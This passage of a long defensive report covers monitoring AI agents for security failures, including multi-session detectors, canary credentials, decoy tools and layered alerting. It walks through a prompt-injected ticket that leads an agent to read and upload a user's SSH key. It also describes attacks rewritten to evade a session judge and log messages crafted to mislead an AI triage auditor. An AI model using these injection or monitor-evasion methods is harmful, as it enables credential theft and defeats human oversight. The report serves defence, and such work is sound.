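- **A session judge** reads one session at a time and flags the scenario if any session breaks the policy.
- **A full-log detector** reads the messages from all the sessions in one long prompt.
- **A memory detector** reads only the 50 entries that a ranking program considers most significant.

In the original version of the benchmark, the session judge caught every attack, so at least one session in each attack was suspicious by itself. Azarafrooz then had a stronger model, Claude Opus 4.7, rewrite each flagged session up to six times until it passed. The rewriter had to keep details such as web addresses and file paths. It succeeded with 90 of 113 sessions.

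| Detector | Original attacks caught, of 26 | Rewritten attacks caught, of 26 | False alarms on ordinary work, of 14 | False alarms on lookalikes, of 14 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Session judge | 26 | 14 | 3 | 9 |
| Full-log detector | 23 | 13 | 0 | 7 |
| Memory detector | 25 | 19 | 0 | 3 |

The judge no longer flagged any session in 12 of the rewritten attacks. (The paper also reports 14, but only 12 fits its results.) The full-log detector caught five of those 12, including a scheme that collects credentials in stages. But it missed six attacks that the judge still caught, apparently because the harmless-looking sessions around them made the whole log seem routine. The longest log filled only 14.8 percent of the model's context window, so lack of space wasn't the cause.

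The memory detector did better on the rewritten attacks, but the evidence that it is better is weak. It caught seven that the full-log detector missed, but missed one that the full-log detector caught. If the two were equally good, a split at least this uneven would occur about 7 percent of the time. Azarafrooz acknowledges that the sample is too small to rank the detectors precisely and that all the models came from one provider.

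The test also favours the memory detector, because the rewriter only had to defeat the session judge. An attacker who knew about the ranking program could try to word every message so that it ranks too low to enter the memory. This might work, since the memory detector missed an identity-switching attack after milder wording pushed the relevant messages out of the top 50.

### Checking intentions before events

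Azarafrooz argues that a SIEM monitors the wrong place. A prompt such as "summarise this configuration file, then send the summary to this address" contains the whole plan before the agent acts, but a SIEM query finds the upload only after the data has gone.

He supports this with a result from information theory. Suppose the attacker's goal *G* shapes the prompt *I*, the prompt shapes what the agent executes, *E*, and the execution produces the log, *L*. If each stage depends only on the one before it, the data processing inequality gives:

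I(G; I) ≥ I(G; E) ≥ I(G; L)

Here I(G; L) is the mutual information between the goal and the log, which measures how much knowing one reduces uncertainty about the other. Under these assumptions, an analyst can't learn more about the attacker's goal from the log than from the prompt.

The assumptions don't fit Dana's case well, because the hostile instruction arrives in the ticket, not in her request. A detector that reads only users' messages would miss it. When an agent overreaches without an attacker, no message contains a hostile goal. A real SIEM also holds records that don't result from the prompt, such as a login from an unfamiliar country just before the session.

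The inequality also covers only the information available to a detector, not how much of it the detector uses. The program selects the 50-entry memory from the full log, so the memory can't contain more information than the log, yet the memory detector caught more attacks. A badly worded plan in a prompt may be harder to recognise than a plain upload in a log.

The best reason to check an agent's intentions early is that only a check before the action can prevent it. Event logs are still the evidence of what happened. If the agent plans to upload Dana's key but the receiving server is down, the prompt looks the same as in a successful theft, so the team needs the connection record to learn whether the key left.

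Loris Degioanni, Sysdig's technology chief, argues in Help Net Security that an agent's account of its own actions is useful context but not evidence, and that a disagreement between that account and the system's record is itself a detection. Sysdig sells products that supply the system record, but his reasoning doesn't depend on them. For example, if a harness log lists `npm test` but the endpoint record shows an upload under the same tool call, an analyst should investigate.

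### Ranking alerts and using a model for triage

Analysts should first see the alerts where a mistake would do the most harm. In Sysdig's example, reading a password for a test environment is noise, while reading the key that administers production is an incident. To rank these alerts, the SIEM needs data on what each secret opens, which it can take from identity governance records. An upload that is still running should also rank above one that EDR blocked.

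In language-model triage, a model reads the alert and the joined records, then returns a verdict with its evidence. Based on the verdict, software closes the alert, queues it or pages an analyst. For the theft of Dana's key, the model would need her request, the ticket's text, the commands, the destination and the agent's registered purpose. An analyst should receive the same records with the model's summary so they can check the summary against them.

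CSTM-Bench is relevant to this method because its full-log detector also reads a log and returns a verdict. The detector raised no false alarms on ordinary work, but it flagged half of the lookalikes and missed half of the rewritten attacks. The test was designed to be difficult, so these rates don't predict how a triage model would perform on a company's usual alerts.

Reading all 54 logs took 2.77 million tokens, or about 51,000 each. At an assumed price of $3 per million tokens, each log would cost about 15 cents, and a thousand alerts of that size around $150. The cost grows faster if the model rereads the history to check each new message. Providers can reuse work on the unchanged beginning of a prompt, but the memory detector's entries often changed order. On average, only 44 percent of the memory stayed in place from one check to the next.

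The model also reads text that an attacker may have written. Azarafrooz describes messages that look harmless separately but form an instruction to the auditor once software joins them into one transcript. In another trick, the attacker uses the last session to claim that everything before it was an authorised drill and to ask for the alert to be withdrawn. He presents the joined instructions as a hazard and doesn't measure how often they succeed. A triage model should never close an alert because of a claim inside the log, since the security team's own calendar will show any real drill.

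Some vendors send uncertain cases to human analysts. Intellyx's *Finding big money for AI and a smaller world for security* (2026) quotes one whose investigating agent does this when it "is not confident". This safeguard fails when the agent dismisses an attack with high confidence, because the case never reaches an analyst. That also seems to have happened in the first stage of Uber's detector.

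A team can estimate this error by having analysts review a random sample of the alerts that the model closed. If they find no attacks among 300, they can be 95 percent confident that attacks make up less than 1 percent of all closed alerts. If the model closes 1,000 alerts a day, it could still be missing up to ten attacks daily, so the team has to keep sampling and review more alerts.

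## Placing decoys and canary credentials where agents will meet them

A decoy can raise an alert from a single event, while a correlation rule has to join several records first. If a laptop holds a fake AWS key that grants no access and someone tries to use it, the security team can start investigating without working out what normal activity looks like.

### Whether the premise holds for agents

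Deception relies on the premise that no legitimate task needs the fake asset, which is mostly true for people. An employee has her own AWS key and hasn't heard or read about the fake one, so anyone who uses the fake key has probably been hunting for credentials.

Vendors apply the same premise to agents. Acalvio's *The OWASP guide to AI agent security (and where deception fits)* (2026) asserts that a correctly configured agent "never touches these assets". The claim is hard to test because Acalvio could say that any agent that touches one is badly configured. Tracebit's *How do I detect an AI agent or MCP client connecting somewhere* (2026) treats contact as "unauthorized by definition", but concedes that a company's own approved coding agents will eventually trigger a decoy and that these alerts are noise. The concession is somewhat more credible because Tracebit sells decoys. *New Features*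 (Smith, 2026), a Tracebit product announcement, says that coding agents on engineers' laptops read everything they can reach, including canaries.

AI agents have ordinary reasons to touch decoys. A coding agent may read a whole folder to understand a project, where a person would open two files. If a login fails, it may look for another credential, much as the agent that Sophos blocked tried one download tool after another. obormot's *Honeypots for AI Agents* adds that an agent may decide that a credential it has found is relevant to its task.

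### What can serve as a decoy

| Decoy | Example | What raises the alert | How a legitimate agent might set it off |
|---|---|---|---|
| Service | A fake login server | A login attempt | It looks for a database and tries every server it finds |
| File | `production-credentials.sql` in a project folder | Someone imports the file into a database | It rebuilds a test database from the files in the folder |
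| Credential | A fake AWS key | Someone tries the key | Its own login has failed |
| Tool | `admin_shell` in the agent's list of tools | A call to the tool | It runs out of other ways to do a hard task |
| MCP server | An unused entry in the agent's settings | A connection to the server | The harness connects to every server on the list |

A decoy's trigger matters because agents don't always open things the way people do. A decoy Word document usually raises its alert when the word processor loads a hidden web address. An agent that extracts the text with a script may read the whole document without setting off the alert.

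*Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) describes a detector built on decoy tools, with five default names including `admin_shell` and `system_key_dump`. It claims that any call to one confirms a prompt injection with 100 percent precision, because no harmless request leads there. The researchers argued for this figure without measuring it and postponed the test that would have checked it. An agent trying to repair a broken server might well call another of the five, `internal_debug_console`. Each decoy tool also takes up space in the prompt and gives the agent one more wrong option.

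A decoy MCP server can avoid some of these accidents. Lenny Zeltser, a security executive and teacher, suggests adding one to the configuration file that Claude Code reads (Zeltser, in *Plant Honeytokens to Detect Intrusions*):

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "billing-archive": { "type": "http", "url": "<canary URL>" }
  }
}
```

The team then lists `billing-archive` under `disabledMcpjsonServers` in a separate settings file, so the company's own harness never connects to it automatically. An intruder who copies the first file and tries the server raises an alert, as does a hijacked agent that calls the address from a shell. But anyone who reads both files can see that the server is switched off.

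Some researchers also build decoys that trap or sabotage the visiting agent, as in *Cloak, Honey, Trap* by Ayzenshteyn, Weiss and Mirsky, but a decoy can raise an alert without doing either.

### Planting a canary credential

A team should start with what the agent can reach and ask where it would look next if it strayed from its task. On Dana's laptop, those places include the file where AWS tools keep their keys. Zeltser suggests putting a fake key in either a separate backup file or a `[backup]` profile inside the real credentials file. The profile is usually better, because an agent that opens the file for the real key also gets the fake one.

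More fakes improve the odds, up to a point. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) models an attacker who sees *m* real credentials and *k* fakes and picks one at random:

P(alert) = k / (m + k)

An agent that picks at random from one real key and three fakes has a 75 percent chance of picking a fake. The researchers call random choice a simple modelling assumption, and it fails if anything gives the real key away. If a hidden instruction names Dana's SSH key by its path, the chance of picking a fake is zero, however many fakes lie beside it.

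The fake credential needs believable surroundings, such as a profile name and region that match the company's other keys. It also needs an entry in a private register that lists its location, the event that triggers it, the person who responds and any software that legitimately accesses it, including backup programs and secret scanners. The register shouldn't be in a wiki or code repository that agents can search.

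Each location should have its own canary credential. Cox (2026), in *Deception and the OpenAI / Hugging Face agentic breach*, recommends a different one for every container, so that an alert identifies the container the key came from. If a hundred machines share one fake key, an alert shows only that someone has searched one of them.

The alert should go to the SIEM with any details the decoy records about the visitor, such as a source address or account, and the team should measure how long it takes to arrive. Zeltser warns that alerts for one widely used type of fake AWS key take 2 to 30 minutes because they pass through AWS's activity log first. Brucato (2026), in *Webinar*, reports that attacking agents in a Tracebit benchmark took an average of 14 minutes to gain administrator rights in a test AWS environment. They set off a canary a median of eight minutes before their first critical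 action, so an alert that took ten minutes to arrive would often have come too late.

A local alert can be faster. obormot describes Snare, a tool that sends an alert when a program on the machine looks up the fake AWS credentials, before any request reaches AWS. But a local hook can't run on an attacker's computer, so it may miss a key that someone has copied and tries elsewhere.

The team also has to decide in advance what the alert will trigger. Software can suspend the agent for a few minutes without affecting anyone else, as long as the agent doesn't run under Dana's account.

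### The *Optional Traps* experiments

In *Optional Traps*, Ghifiardi (2026) tested how much decoys add once a company has fixed the underlying weakness. His isolated lab contained a mock web service with synthetic records, which anyone with the right key could export. The service had one deliberate flaw, a debug page that displayed the real key. The attacker was a language-model agent that could send web requests to the service and use any credential it found.

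In the first study, Ghifiardi left the flaw open and placed decoys beside it, including a backup file containing a canary key and an old internal API listed where a visitor would find it. In one version of the test, the API returned endless pages to explore. A model with 9.7 billion parameters ignored all the decoys in both versions. It read the real key from the debug page and exported the records with six requests in about a minute.

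Ghifiardi ran each version only once, so the results establish little about the size of any effect. In a third session, with no decoys, the same model found the key but tried the wrong export addresses until its time ran out. Taken at face value, the three sessions would suggest that decoys help attackers. They do show that an agent with a working route to its goal can bypass a decoy.

For the second study, Ghifiardi put the bait where the leak had been. He used a smaller model, with 4 billion parameters, in 60 sessions divided equally among three conditions:

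| Condition | What the debug page returned | Successful exports | Attacking client cut off |
|---|---|---|---|
| Baseline | The real key | 20 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Hardening alone | "Not found" | 0 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Hardening plus decoy | A canary key | 0 of 20 | 19 of 20 |

When the agent used the canary key, a gateway in front of the service refused all requests from that client for 15 minutes. In the one session without a revocation, the agent read the bait but presented a different credential, which the service didn't recognise.

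The difference between the baseline and the other two conditions is far too large to be chance, but the true rates are less certain. Zero exports in 20 sessions is compatible with a success rate of up to 16.1 percent, and 19 revocations with a rate of about 76 to 99 percent. Ghifiardi had also told the agent which addresses to explore and where to request the export, so an attacker who has to find the debug page unaided might meet the bait less often.

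### Turning an alert into a revocation

Ghifiardi's third study tested whether an alert from a decoy could cut off a client automatically. It ran on a Google Cloud machine and used OpenCanary, an open-source program that imitates services such as login servers. A script played the attacker, with no model involved. Ghifiardi gave the script a valid key so that only the alert could stop it.

The script first used the key successfully, then tried to log in to the fake server. OpenCanary recorded the attempt and sent an alert to a small adapter program. The adapter checked that the alert came from the sensor's address, removed the password, signed the alert and passed it to the gateway. The gateway blocked the client 13 milliseconds after OpenCanary recorded the login attempt. When the script next tried to export the records, the gateway refused, although the key was still valid. A legitimate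 client made 100 requests after the revocation, and all of them succeeded.

The first refusal came at most 303 milliseconds after the login began. An earlier version of the gateway took at most 266 milliseconds. Each figure is a single observation with every component running on one machine, so the method can be fast, but we can't tell from these figures how fast it would be across a company's network.

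The security checks are as important as the speed, because an attacker who could forge an alert could use it to lock out legitimate users. The gateway rejected a forged alert, an alert with an invalid signature, and a repeat of a genuine alert. It also kept refusing the blocked client when that client claimed another identity in a request header. However, it identified clients by network address, which Ghifiardi notes could cut off innocent clients who share the attacker's address.

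An agent may take much longer to touch the bait than the gateway takes to respond. In the fourth study, agents with their own signed identities attacked the service in teams. In one engagement, the gateway cut off three of the five attacking agents, 39, 54 and 59 seconds after serving them the bait. It denied their 58 later requests and didn't block the other two agents. None of the agents exported any records, but all 90 of their export requests had gone to an address that didn't exist, so the lack of exports can't be credited to the defence.

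Each engagement also included one legitimate agent. In one, the agent had the correct key in its prompt but fetched the debug page and used the key it found there instead. The gateway cut it off as it would an attacker. In another, the legitimate agent saw the bait and did not use it. These were single engagements with the same two small models, so they show that a legitimate agent can take the bait but not how often this happens.

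### Decoys as prevention

Ghifiardi concludes that hardening prevented the exports and that the decoys added detection. His design almost guaranteed the first finding. Once the debug page stopped giving out the real key, the lab had no other planted weakness to exploit. Hardening alone reduced exports to zero, leaving none for the decoys to prevent.

A test of whether decoys prevent attacks has to leave a real weakness open. *A Gingerbread House for LLM Agents* (2026) reports such a test of AgentTrap, which places decoy addresses beside a vulnerable one. Attack success fell from 95.8 to 79.2 percent. The paper reports a better result for AgentSnare, which leaves a trail of clues to a simulated machine. No agent exploited the real target in 15 benchmark tasks with three attempts at each.

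Part of the difficulty is that an agent can pursue the decoy and the real target at once. *Hacking the Hackers* (2026), a white paper from the security company Horizon3.ai, summarises an experiment in which 21 models read descriptions of systems and marked the lines they would attack. Decoys reduced the human participants' attacks on real weaknesses by 22 percent but had no statistically detectable effect on the models'. The models didn't run live attacks, so marking both the decoy and the real weakness may have carried no penalty. Ghifiardi's gateway, by contrast, cut an agent off after one mistake.

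Suspecting that decoys are present may also slow an attacker. Cox quotes OpenAI's advice, given at the Black Hat security conference, that decoys make agents unsure which credentials are safe to use. According to Smith, Tracebit's tests found that telling attacking agents that deception might be present cut the rate of full compromise from 20 to 3 percent. A defender doesn't normally write the attacker's prompt, so this result is better evidence of how suspicious agents behave than of what decoys do. A suspicious agent may also avoid the canary, leaving the team without an alert.

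The evidence therefore supports fixing a weakness first and then putting a canary in its place.

### How much an alert proves

Acalvio describes contact with its decoys as giving "definitive threat signals". Even a small rate of innocent contact would undermine that claim. If a company ran 10,000 agent sessions a day and legitimate agents touched a decoy in one session out of 1,000, it would get about 300 false alerts a month. If one real attack also set off a decoy that month, any given alert would have about a 0.3 percent chance of being the real one. At one innocent contact per million sessions, that chance would be about 77 percent. Nobody has published the real rate for a company's own agents, so a team has to measure it.

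The strength of the evidence also depends on what the visitor did. Reading a fake key is weak evidence when agents read whole folders. Trying to use it is much stronger evidence, because the agent has to choose that key for some purpose. The legitimate agent that saw Ghifiardi's bait and left it alone would have caused a false alert if reading alone triggered one. But if the alert waits until someone tries to use the key, that key and any real ones stored with it may already have left the company.

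Ghifiardi recommends treating the use of bait as strong but not conclusive evidence, and favours responses that are limited to one client and easy to reverse. A 15-minute suspension fits this well because it delays a harmless agent only briefly and gives an analyst time to read the agent's prompt and tool calls before a harmful one can continue.

Decoy alerts can be useful even when they don't identify the cause. In April 2025, an intruder used a vulnerable automated workflow to obtain access tokens from Grafana Labs, a software company. According to Grafana Labs' *Canary tokens* (2025), canary tokens revealed the intruder's activity. The company found no changes to its code and no exposure of customer data.

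### Keeping decoys out of legitimate agents' way

Tracebit handles false alerts by letting customers register their approved agents. It then labels each AI-related alert "sanctioned" or "unsanctioned", and its configuration instructs approved agents to avoid the canaries. The labels help a team find unregistered agents. But a team that closes every "sanctioned" alert could miss Dana's hijacked agent, which is approved, just as it could by exempting the whole agent from endpoint rules.

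Teaching agents to avoid canaries has a similar drawback. If an agent still avoids them after a hidden instruction has taken it over, it will steal the real key and leave the fake one alone. If the agent's configuration names the canaries, an attacker who gets the agent to reveal it learns which credentials to avoid.

Careful placement prevents many accidental alerts without giving the agent any such information. Coding agents do most of their legitimate work in the project folder, so a canary elsewhere in the home directory should cause fewer false alerts than one beside the source code. Zeltser calls decoy web links in documentation the noisiest type, because people click on them and automated indexers follow every link. On machines that several developers share, obormot points out, someone may also find a planted credential and use it for real work.

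Fake records are the riskiest decoys for an agent's own work. Acalvio recommends planting them in an agent's memory and in the document collections it searches. But search software selects records that resemble the question, so a fake one can turn up without the agent doing anything wrong. If Dana asks how many customers reported login failures this month, a fake ticket could add one to the answer. Decoy tickets need a marker that the agent can't see but that reporting software can use to exclude them.

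### What makes a fake credential believable

Weinberg (2026) argues in *PHANTOM* that most fake credentials have the right format but lack company-specific details. His program uses details from a company profile throughout each fake, including the company's domain, service names, database and cloud region. For a fictional payments company called Payflow, it gives a fake AWS key the account name `payflow_payments_api_deploy`, where an ordinary template might use a generic administrator name.

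Weinberg generated 32 decoy credentials with PHANTOM and 32 from templates, covering eight types and four fictional companies. He scored each from 0 to 1 on its format, how well it fit the company, how random its characters were and how likely a human was to accept it. PHANTOM averaged 0.778 and the templates 0.576. Their format scores hardly differed, and PHANTOM's largest measured gain was in fit with the company.

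The paper also reports that "human acceptance" rose from 6.2 to 100 percent, but no people judged the credentials. The figure is the share of credentials with an overall score of at least 0.65, so it isn't independent evidence for that score. The scoring rules also reward company names, which PHANTOM inserts by design. The remaining evidence comes from three simulated scanners, which flagged 13 percent of PHANTOM's credentials and 39 percent of the templates. One scanner looks for generic phrases such as "example.com", which PHANTOM removes.

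PHANTOM's published procedure for fake AWS key IDs puts 17 characters after the standard prefix `AKIA`, and its format check uses the same length, but real ones normally have 16. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* lists length among the signs that give fakes away, along with prefixes, checksums and unusual randomness. An invented key also raises no alert when someone tries it, because AWS has no account to connect it with. A working canary needs a real key, issued to an account with no permissions.

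Weinberg's main idea is still sensible, but his experiment doesn't show that it deceives anyone. A team can test this more directly by giving an agent four real-looking test keys and one canary, then asking it to pick out the canary. Over many trials, an agent that can't tell them apart should be right about 20 percent of the time.

Other evidence suggests that decoys don't have to be convincing to attract many agents. In the Horizon3.ai experiment, the models took the bait 78.5 percent of the time, compared with 37 percent for human security testers. Models often described something as a probable trap but marked it for attack anyway. The white paper therefore advises defenders to make bait obvious and plant it everywhere.

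The security training organisation SANS passes on advice to deploy decoys liberally because agents can't easily distinguish them from real systems. This may hold for an agent that hasn't been told what to look for, but an attacker can easily add a list of clues to its prompt. *Say Shibboleth* (2026) reports that an automated attacker called Rouxii correctly identified open-source decoy systems 19 percent of the time with an ordinary prompt, and 97 percent of the time when its prompt listed specific clues. Obvious bait is also more likely to attract a company's own agents.

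### Maintaining decoys

Decoys become less convincing as the systems around them change. Tracebit gives the example of a credential unused for six months, which stands out among keys that programs use every day. Weinberg acknowledges that PHANTOM's fixed company profile has the same problem when teams rename services or move to another cloud region. He suggests generating the profile from a company's infrastructure configuration files. Attackers can also learn to recognize a particular provider's decoys. Zeltser notes that researchers have catalogued the signs of canaries hosted by Thinkst, a popular provider, and recommends that companies facing sophisticated attackers host their own.

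New models can make old decoy tests obsolete. Tracebit's *Making attacking agents pay* (2026) reports that more capable models are harder to deceive and that decoys need constant testing. Tracebit would benefit from selling that testing, but the Rouxii result also suggests that a decoy that works on one agent may not work on another.

A team can test its decoys whenever it adopts a new model or gives an agent new tools. Running the agent on ordinary tasks and counting how often it touches a decoy gives the false-positive rate. The team can then plant a hostile instruction in a test ticket and see whether the agent meets a decoy before it reaches anything valuable. If the agent goes straight to a real key, the team should protect that key first and then move the decoy. The team should also trigger each canary by hand periodically, because a canary whose alert no longer works looks the same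 as one that nobody has touched.

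## Combining the layers and deciding what each may do

A team with all five kinds of record still has to decide which one to rely on for each type of failure, and which actions an alert from each is allowed to trigger.

### Which layer covers which failure

In the table below, "prevents" means a layer can stop the harm, "detects" means it can raise an alert, and "explains" means it can show why the agent acted. "May" means the result depends heavily on configuration or on what the agent happens to touch. The entries are judgements based on the cases in earlier sections, because there doesn't seem to be a published test of all five layers on the same attacks.

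| Failure | Identity governance | EDR | Agent record and intent check | SIEM | Decoys |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unknown agent | May detect its OAuth grant | Detects, may prevent | Sees nothing | May detect its sign-ins | May detect |
| Excess access | Prevents | Sees nothing | Explains what the task needs | May detect unused access | Sees nothing |
| Injected instruction | May prevent | May detect | Prevents, explains | May detect | May detect |
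| Overreach without an attacker | May prevent | May detect | Prevents, explains | May detect | May detect |
| Stolen credential used elsewhere | May prevent | Sees nothing | Explains how it left | Detects | Detects if it is a fake |
| Slow activity across sessions | May prevent | May detect single steps | Explains single steps | May detect | May detect |
| Action inside a cloud service | May prevent | Sees nothing | May prevent, explains | Detects, with the service's logs | May detect |

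The agent record provides most of the explanation for an agent's actions, but it doesn't cover unknown agents, because nobody has connected their harnesses. EDR can find an unregistered agent on a laptop but doesn't record what an agent does inside a cloud service.

Slow activity has the weakest coverage in the table. An expired permission may end the attack by accident, and a decoy may catch one step, but only the SIEM can connect the sessions, and it often lacks the fields to do so. Research also has gaps. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) sorted published defences by the part of the system they protect and the timing of the attack, and found none for 7 of the 28 combinations.

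### Ticket 4711 with every layer in place

Suppose Dana's company has installed all five layers, and the ticket tells her agent to steal her SSH key. Each layer gets its chance at a different moment:

| Moment | What could intervene | Result if it works |
|---|---|---|
| Before the request | Identity governance has put the agent in a container without Dana's key | There is nothing to steal |
| 10:02:11, the ticket arrives | A scan for prompt injection | The agent never reads the instruction |
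| 10:02:40, `cat` opens the key | An intent check, or an EDR rule for secret files | The key stays on the laptop |
| 10:03:05, `curl` connects | An intent check on the upload command, or an EDR block | The attacker gets nothing |
| Shortly afterwards | The SIEM rule that joins the three events | The team can replace the key before anyone uses it |
| Hours or days later | A canary credential that the agent copied along with the key | The team learns that someone is trying stolen credentials |

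After 10:03:05 the company can no longer keep the key secret, but it can replace the key so that the old one stops working. If the intent check stops the upload but not the read, the team should still replace the key, because it has probably reached the model provider in the next prompt.

When the hidden instruction targets another customer's ticket instead, most of these chances disappear. The company then depends on a token limited to ticket 4711, the intent check, or a baseline that flags a second customer's ticket.

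### What two detectors catch between them

Suppose a company runs 10,000 agent sessions a day, one of which is harmful, and uses two detectors. Detector A catches 90 percent of harmful sessions and wrongly flags 1 percent of harmless ones. Detector B catches 80 percent and wrongly flags 0.5 percent.

Detector A alone raises about 100 false alarms a day, so fewer than one in a hundred of its alerts is real. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, argued that the false alarm rate is the limiting factor for an intrusion detector because attacks are so rare among ordinary events, and this is still true with AI agents.

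The usual argument for adding a second detector is that miss rates multiply, as *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) sets out, with the warning that the sum needs correcting where the layers don't fail independently. If A and B are independent:

- **Alert on either:** detection is 1 − (0.10 × 0.20) = 98 percent, with 9,999 × (1 − 0.99 × 0.995) ≈ 150 false alarms a day.
- **Alert only on both:** detection is 0.90 × 0.80 = 72 percent, with 9,999 × 0.01 × 0.005 ≈ 0.5 false alarms a day, or one every two days.

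The other extreme is complete overlap, where A also misses nothing that B catches and every false alarm from B also sets off A.

| Alert rule | Attacks detected | False alarms a day | Share of alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| A alone | 90% | 100 | 0.9% |
| B alone | 80% | 50 | 1.6% |
| Either, independent | 98% | 150 | 0.7% |
| Both, independent | 72% | 0.5 | 59% |
| Either, complete overlap | 90% | 100 | 0.9% |
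| Both, complete overlap | 80% | 50 | 1.6% |

The benefit of requiring both detectors to fire depends most on how independent their false alarms are. If one in ten of B's false alarms also set off A, instead of one in a hundred, the company would get five false alarms a day, and only about 13 percent of its alerts would be real.

### Why detectors fail together

One cause is a shared data source. Suppose A and B both read the harness log, and the log is missing for 5 percent of harmful sessions. Even if their misses are independent in the other sessions, alerting when either one fires catches about 94 percent of attacks instead of 98, so the misses nearly triple. A and B still catch 90 and 80 percent individually, so testing them separately wouldn't reveal the problem.

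The second cause is a shared method. *Builder, Defender, Breaker* (2026) cites an experiment by Knight and Leveson in which independently written programs failed on the same inputs far more often than chance would predict, because people with similar training make similar mistakes on the hard parts of a problem. It also cites a newer study of programs written by twelve language models, in which combining five programs by majority vote improved reliability less than half as much as it would have if the programs had failed independently.

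*Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer* (Yang, 2026) measures how often different software checks on agents' actions miss the same ones. It tests a set of 174 fixed text-matching rules and four language-model judges on 560 actions that they should have blocked. Two of the judges each missed 10.5 percent of the actions. If their misses were independent, both would have missed the same action in about 1.1 percent of cases, but this happened in 5.2 percent. The rules missed 13.4 percent of the actions, but the rules and one of those judges both missed only 1.3 percent, close to the 1.4 percent expected if their misses were independent.

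Layers that read the same source don't always make the same mistakes. The rules and the judges all read the text of the proposed action, but their difference in method mattered more here. Using a judge from a different vendor helped little, because judges from different vendors tended to miss the same cases.

Yang also found that improving one detector may not improve the combination. An extra pack of cloud rules cut the rules' own miss rate from 13.9 to 11.1 percent, counting referrals to a person as misses, but every group of three judges already caught the additional cases.

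These results don't show that fixed rules are enough. On a separate set of 87 actions involving cloud services and software supply chains, the rules missed 52.9 percent. On another team's collection of risky shell commands, where every detector missed most cases, the rules and judges were only about halfway between complete overlap and independence. Yang didn't test an attacker who adapts, and someone who knows the rules can write a command that none of them matches.

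A team should therefore choose a second detector that uses a different method and, if possible, a different source, then run both detectors on the same test attacks and count the attacks that both miss. With 300 attacks, a joint miss rate of 2 percent would produce about six misses and a rate of 6 percent about 18, which is usually enough to tell the two rates apart. Thirty attacks would be too few to distinguish them from chance variation.

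### Which alert may trigger which response

A weak signal can justify a cheap response that is easy to undo, while an expensive response needs stronger evidence.

| Response | Signal that is usually enough | Cost of a mistake | How to undo it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Log the event | Anything unusual, such as an agent opening a decoy file | Storage and search time | Nothing to undo |
| Ask a person | An uncertain intent verdict, or an action nobody can reverse | A minute of attention, and more habitual approvals | Change the answer before the action runs |
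| Block one action | A clear mismatch with the task, or a fixed rule such as a secret in a prompt | The agent tries another way or stops | Allow the action and repeat it |
| Revoke a credential | Someone tries a canary, or one credential is in use on two machines | Everything that relies on the credential stops | Issue a new one |
| Isolate a machine | Two different sources point to an intruder or a program that keeps restarting | The user loses the machine for hours | Reconnect it after an inspection |

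The choice can be put as a simple calculation. Let *p* be the probability that the alert is real, *c* the cost of acting when it isn't, and *h* the harm that acting prevents when it is. Acting costs (1 − *p*)*c* on average through mistakes, and waiting costs *ph*. Acting is worth it when:

p > c / (c + h)

Suppose, again for illustration, that a wrong block wastes two minutes, wrongly isolating Dana's laptop wastes four hours, and either response saves 100 hours of repair when the alert is real. Blocking is worthwhile if the chance that the alert is real exceeds about 0.03 percent, and isolation if it exceeds about 3.8 percent. An alert from detector A, which is real 0.9 percent of the time, is enough to block an action but not to isolate a laptop. If A and B are independent, an alert from both has a 59 percent chance of being real, which justifies isolation. If they overlap completely, the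 chance is only 1.6 percent, which does not. A company that isolates machines automatically therefore needs to know whether its detectors are independent or overlap.

Suspension is a useful step before revocation. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes four states for an agent's credentials: registered, active, suspended and retired. Suspending or retiring an agent instead of deleting it preserves the audit record, and an analyst can reactivate a suspended agent without setting it up again.

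Human review protects the company only if someone answers the request. One of Yang's judges flagged 47 of the 560 cases for human review. It missed 1.4 percent of the actions if those flags count as catches, and 9.8 percent if they count as misses. A company with nobody on duty at night should use the 9.8 percent figure for those hours.

The software also has to wait for the person's answer, and much of it can run other actions in the meantime. *Stop Means Stop* (Khan, 2026) tested six open-source frameworks for building agents. Five can pause for approval before an action: LangGraph, its JavaScript version, LlamaIndex Workflows, Microsoft Agent Framework and the OpenAI Agents SDK. In all five, the pause held up only its own branch of the work. If the agent requested two actions in parallel and one needed approval, the other could run while the person was still deciding.

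For example, if Dana's agent asks to send a reply and uploads an attachment at the same time, the upload can finish before she sees the request. Live models on unmodified frameworks caused such leaks in 215 of 1,200 runs. In more natural customer-service tasks, though, the models made their changes one at a time, so the flaw appeared only when an injected instruction triggered it. Khan also found that actions could finish after the framework had reported a cancellation or a timeout.

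Khan's remedy is a gate outside the framework that every action with an outside effect must pass through. His version blocked all the failures he had measured and added about a millisecond to each write. The gate works only if the agent can't bypass it. A team can test its own approval step by having the agent run two harmless actions in parallel, one that needs approval and one that writes a file. If the file appears before anyone answers the approval request, the approval step doesn't pause the whole agent.

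### Hourly collection, inline hooks and revocation

The theft of Dana's key took 54 seconds from the ticket to the upload, a useful benchmark for each method's speed.

| Method | Delay | Effect on the theft | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hourly collection | About 30 minutes on average, plus analysis | Finds it afterwards | The key has already left |
| Inline hook | The action waits for the verdict | Can prevent it | Covers only the steps that the harness exposes |
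| Revocation | Seconds to hours, depending on the service | Limits later use | Issued tokens and queued work may continue |

Hourly collection is still useful because it gives a detector the whole session to read and plenty of time to analyze it. The slower stage of Uber's detector averaged 29.7 seconds, which is fine after the event but too long before every tool call. Li and colleagues, who use hooks only to block secrets, note that simple pattern checks suit known strings such as keys but fail when detection requires understanding a tool's function or company policy.

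Revocation described as instant often takes effect after a delay. Insinuator's *Token Theft in Microsoft Entra ID (Part 2 of 4)* (2026) explains that a token already issued normally works until it expires. Microsoft gives the default lifetime as one hour.

Microsoft's remedy, continuous access evaluation, notifies supported services when an account is disabled or an administrator revokes its sessions. Microsoft aims for near real time but warns that delays can reach 15 minutes, and changes to access policies or group membership can take up to a day. According to Collab365 Spaces' *Risky Entra apps can lose access tokens within minutes* (2026), Microsoft has extended the method to some software accounts, which can now lose access to Microsoft Graph, the interface to its cloud data, within a few minutes instead of 60 to 90 minutes. The feature is limited in scope and by licensing.

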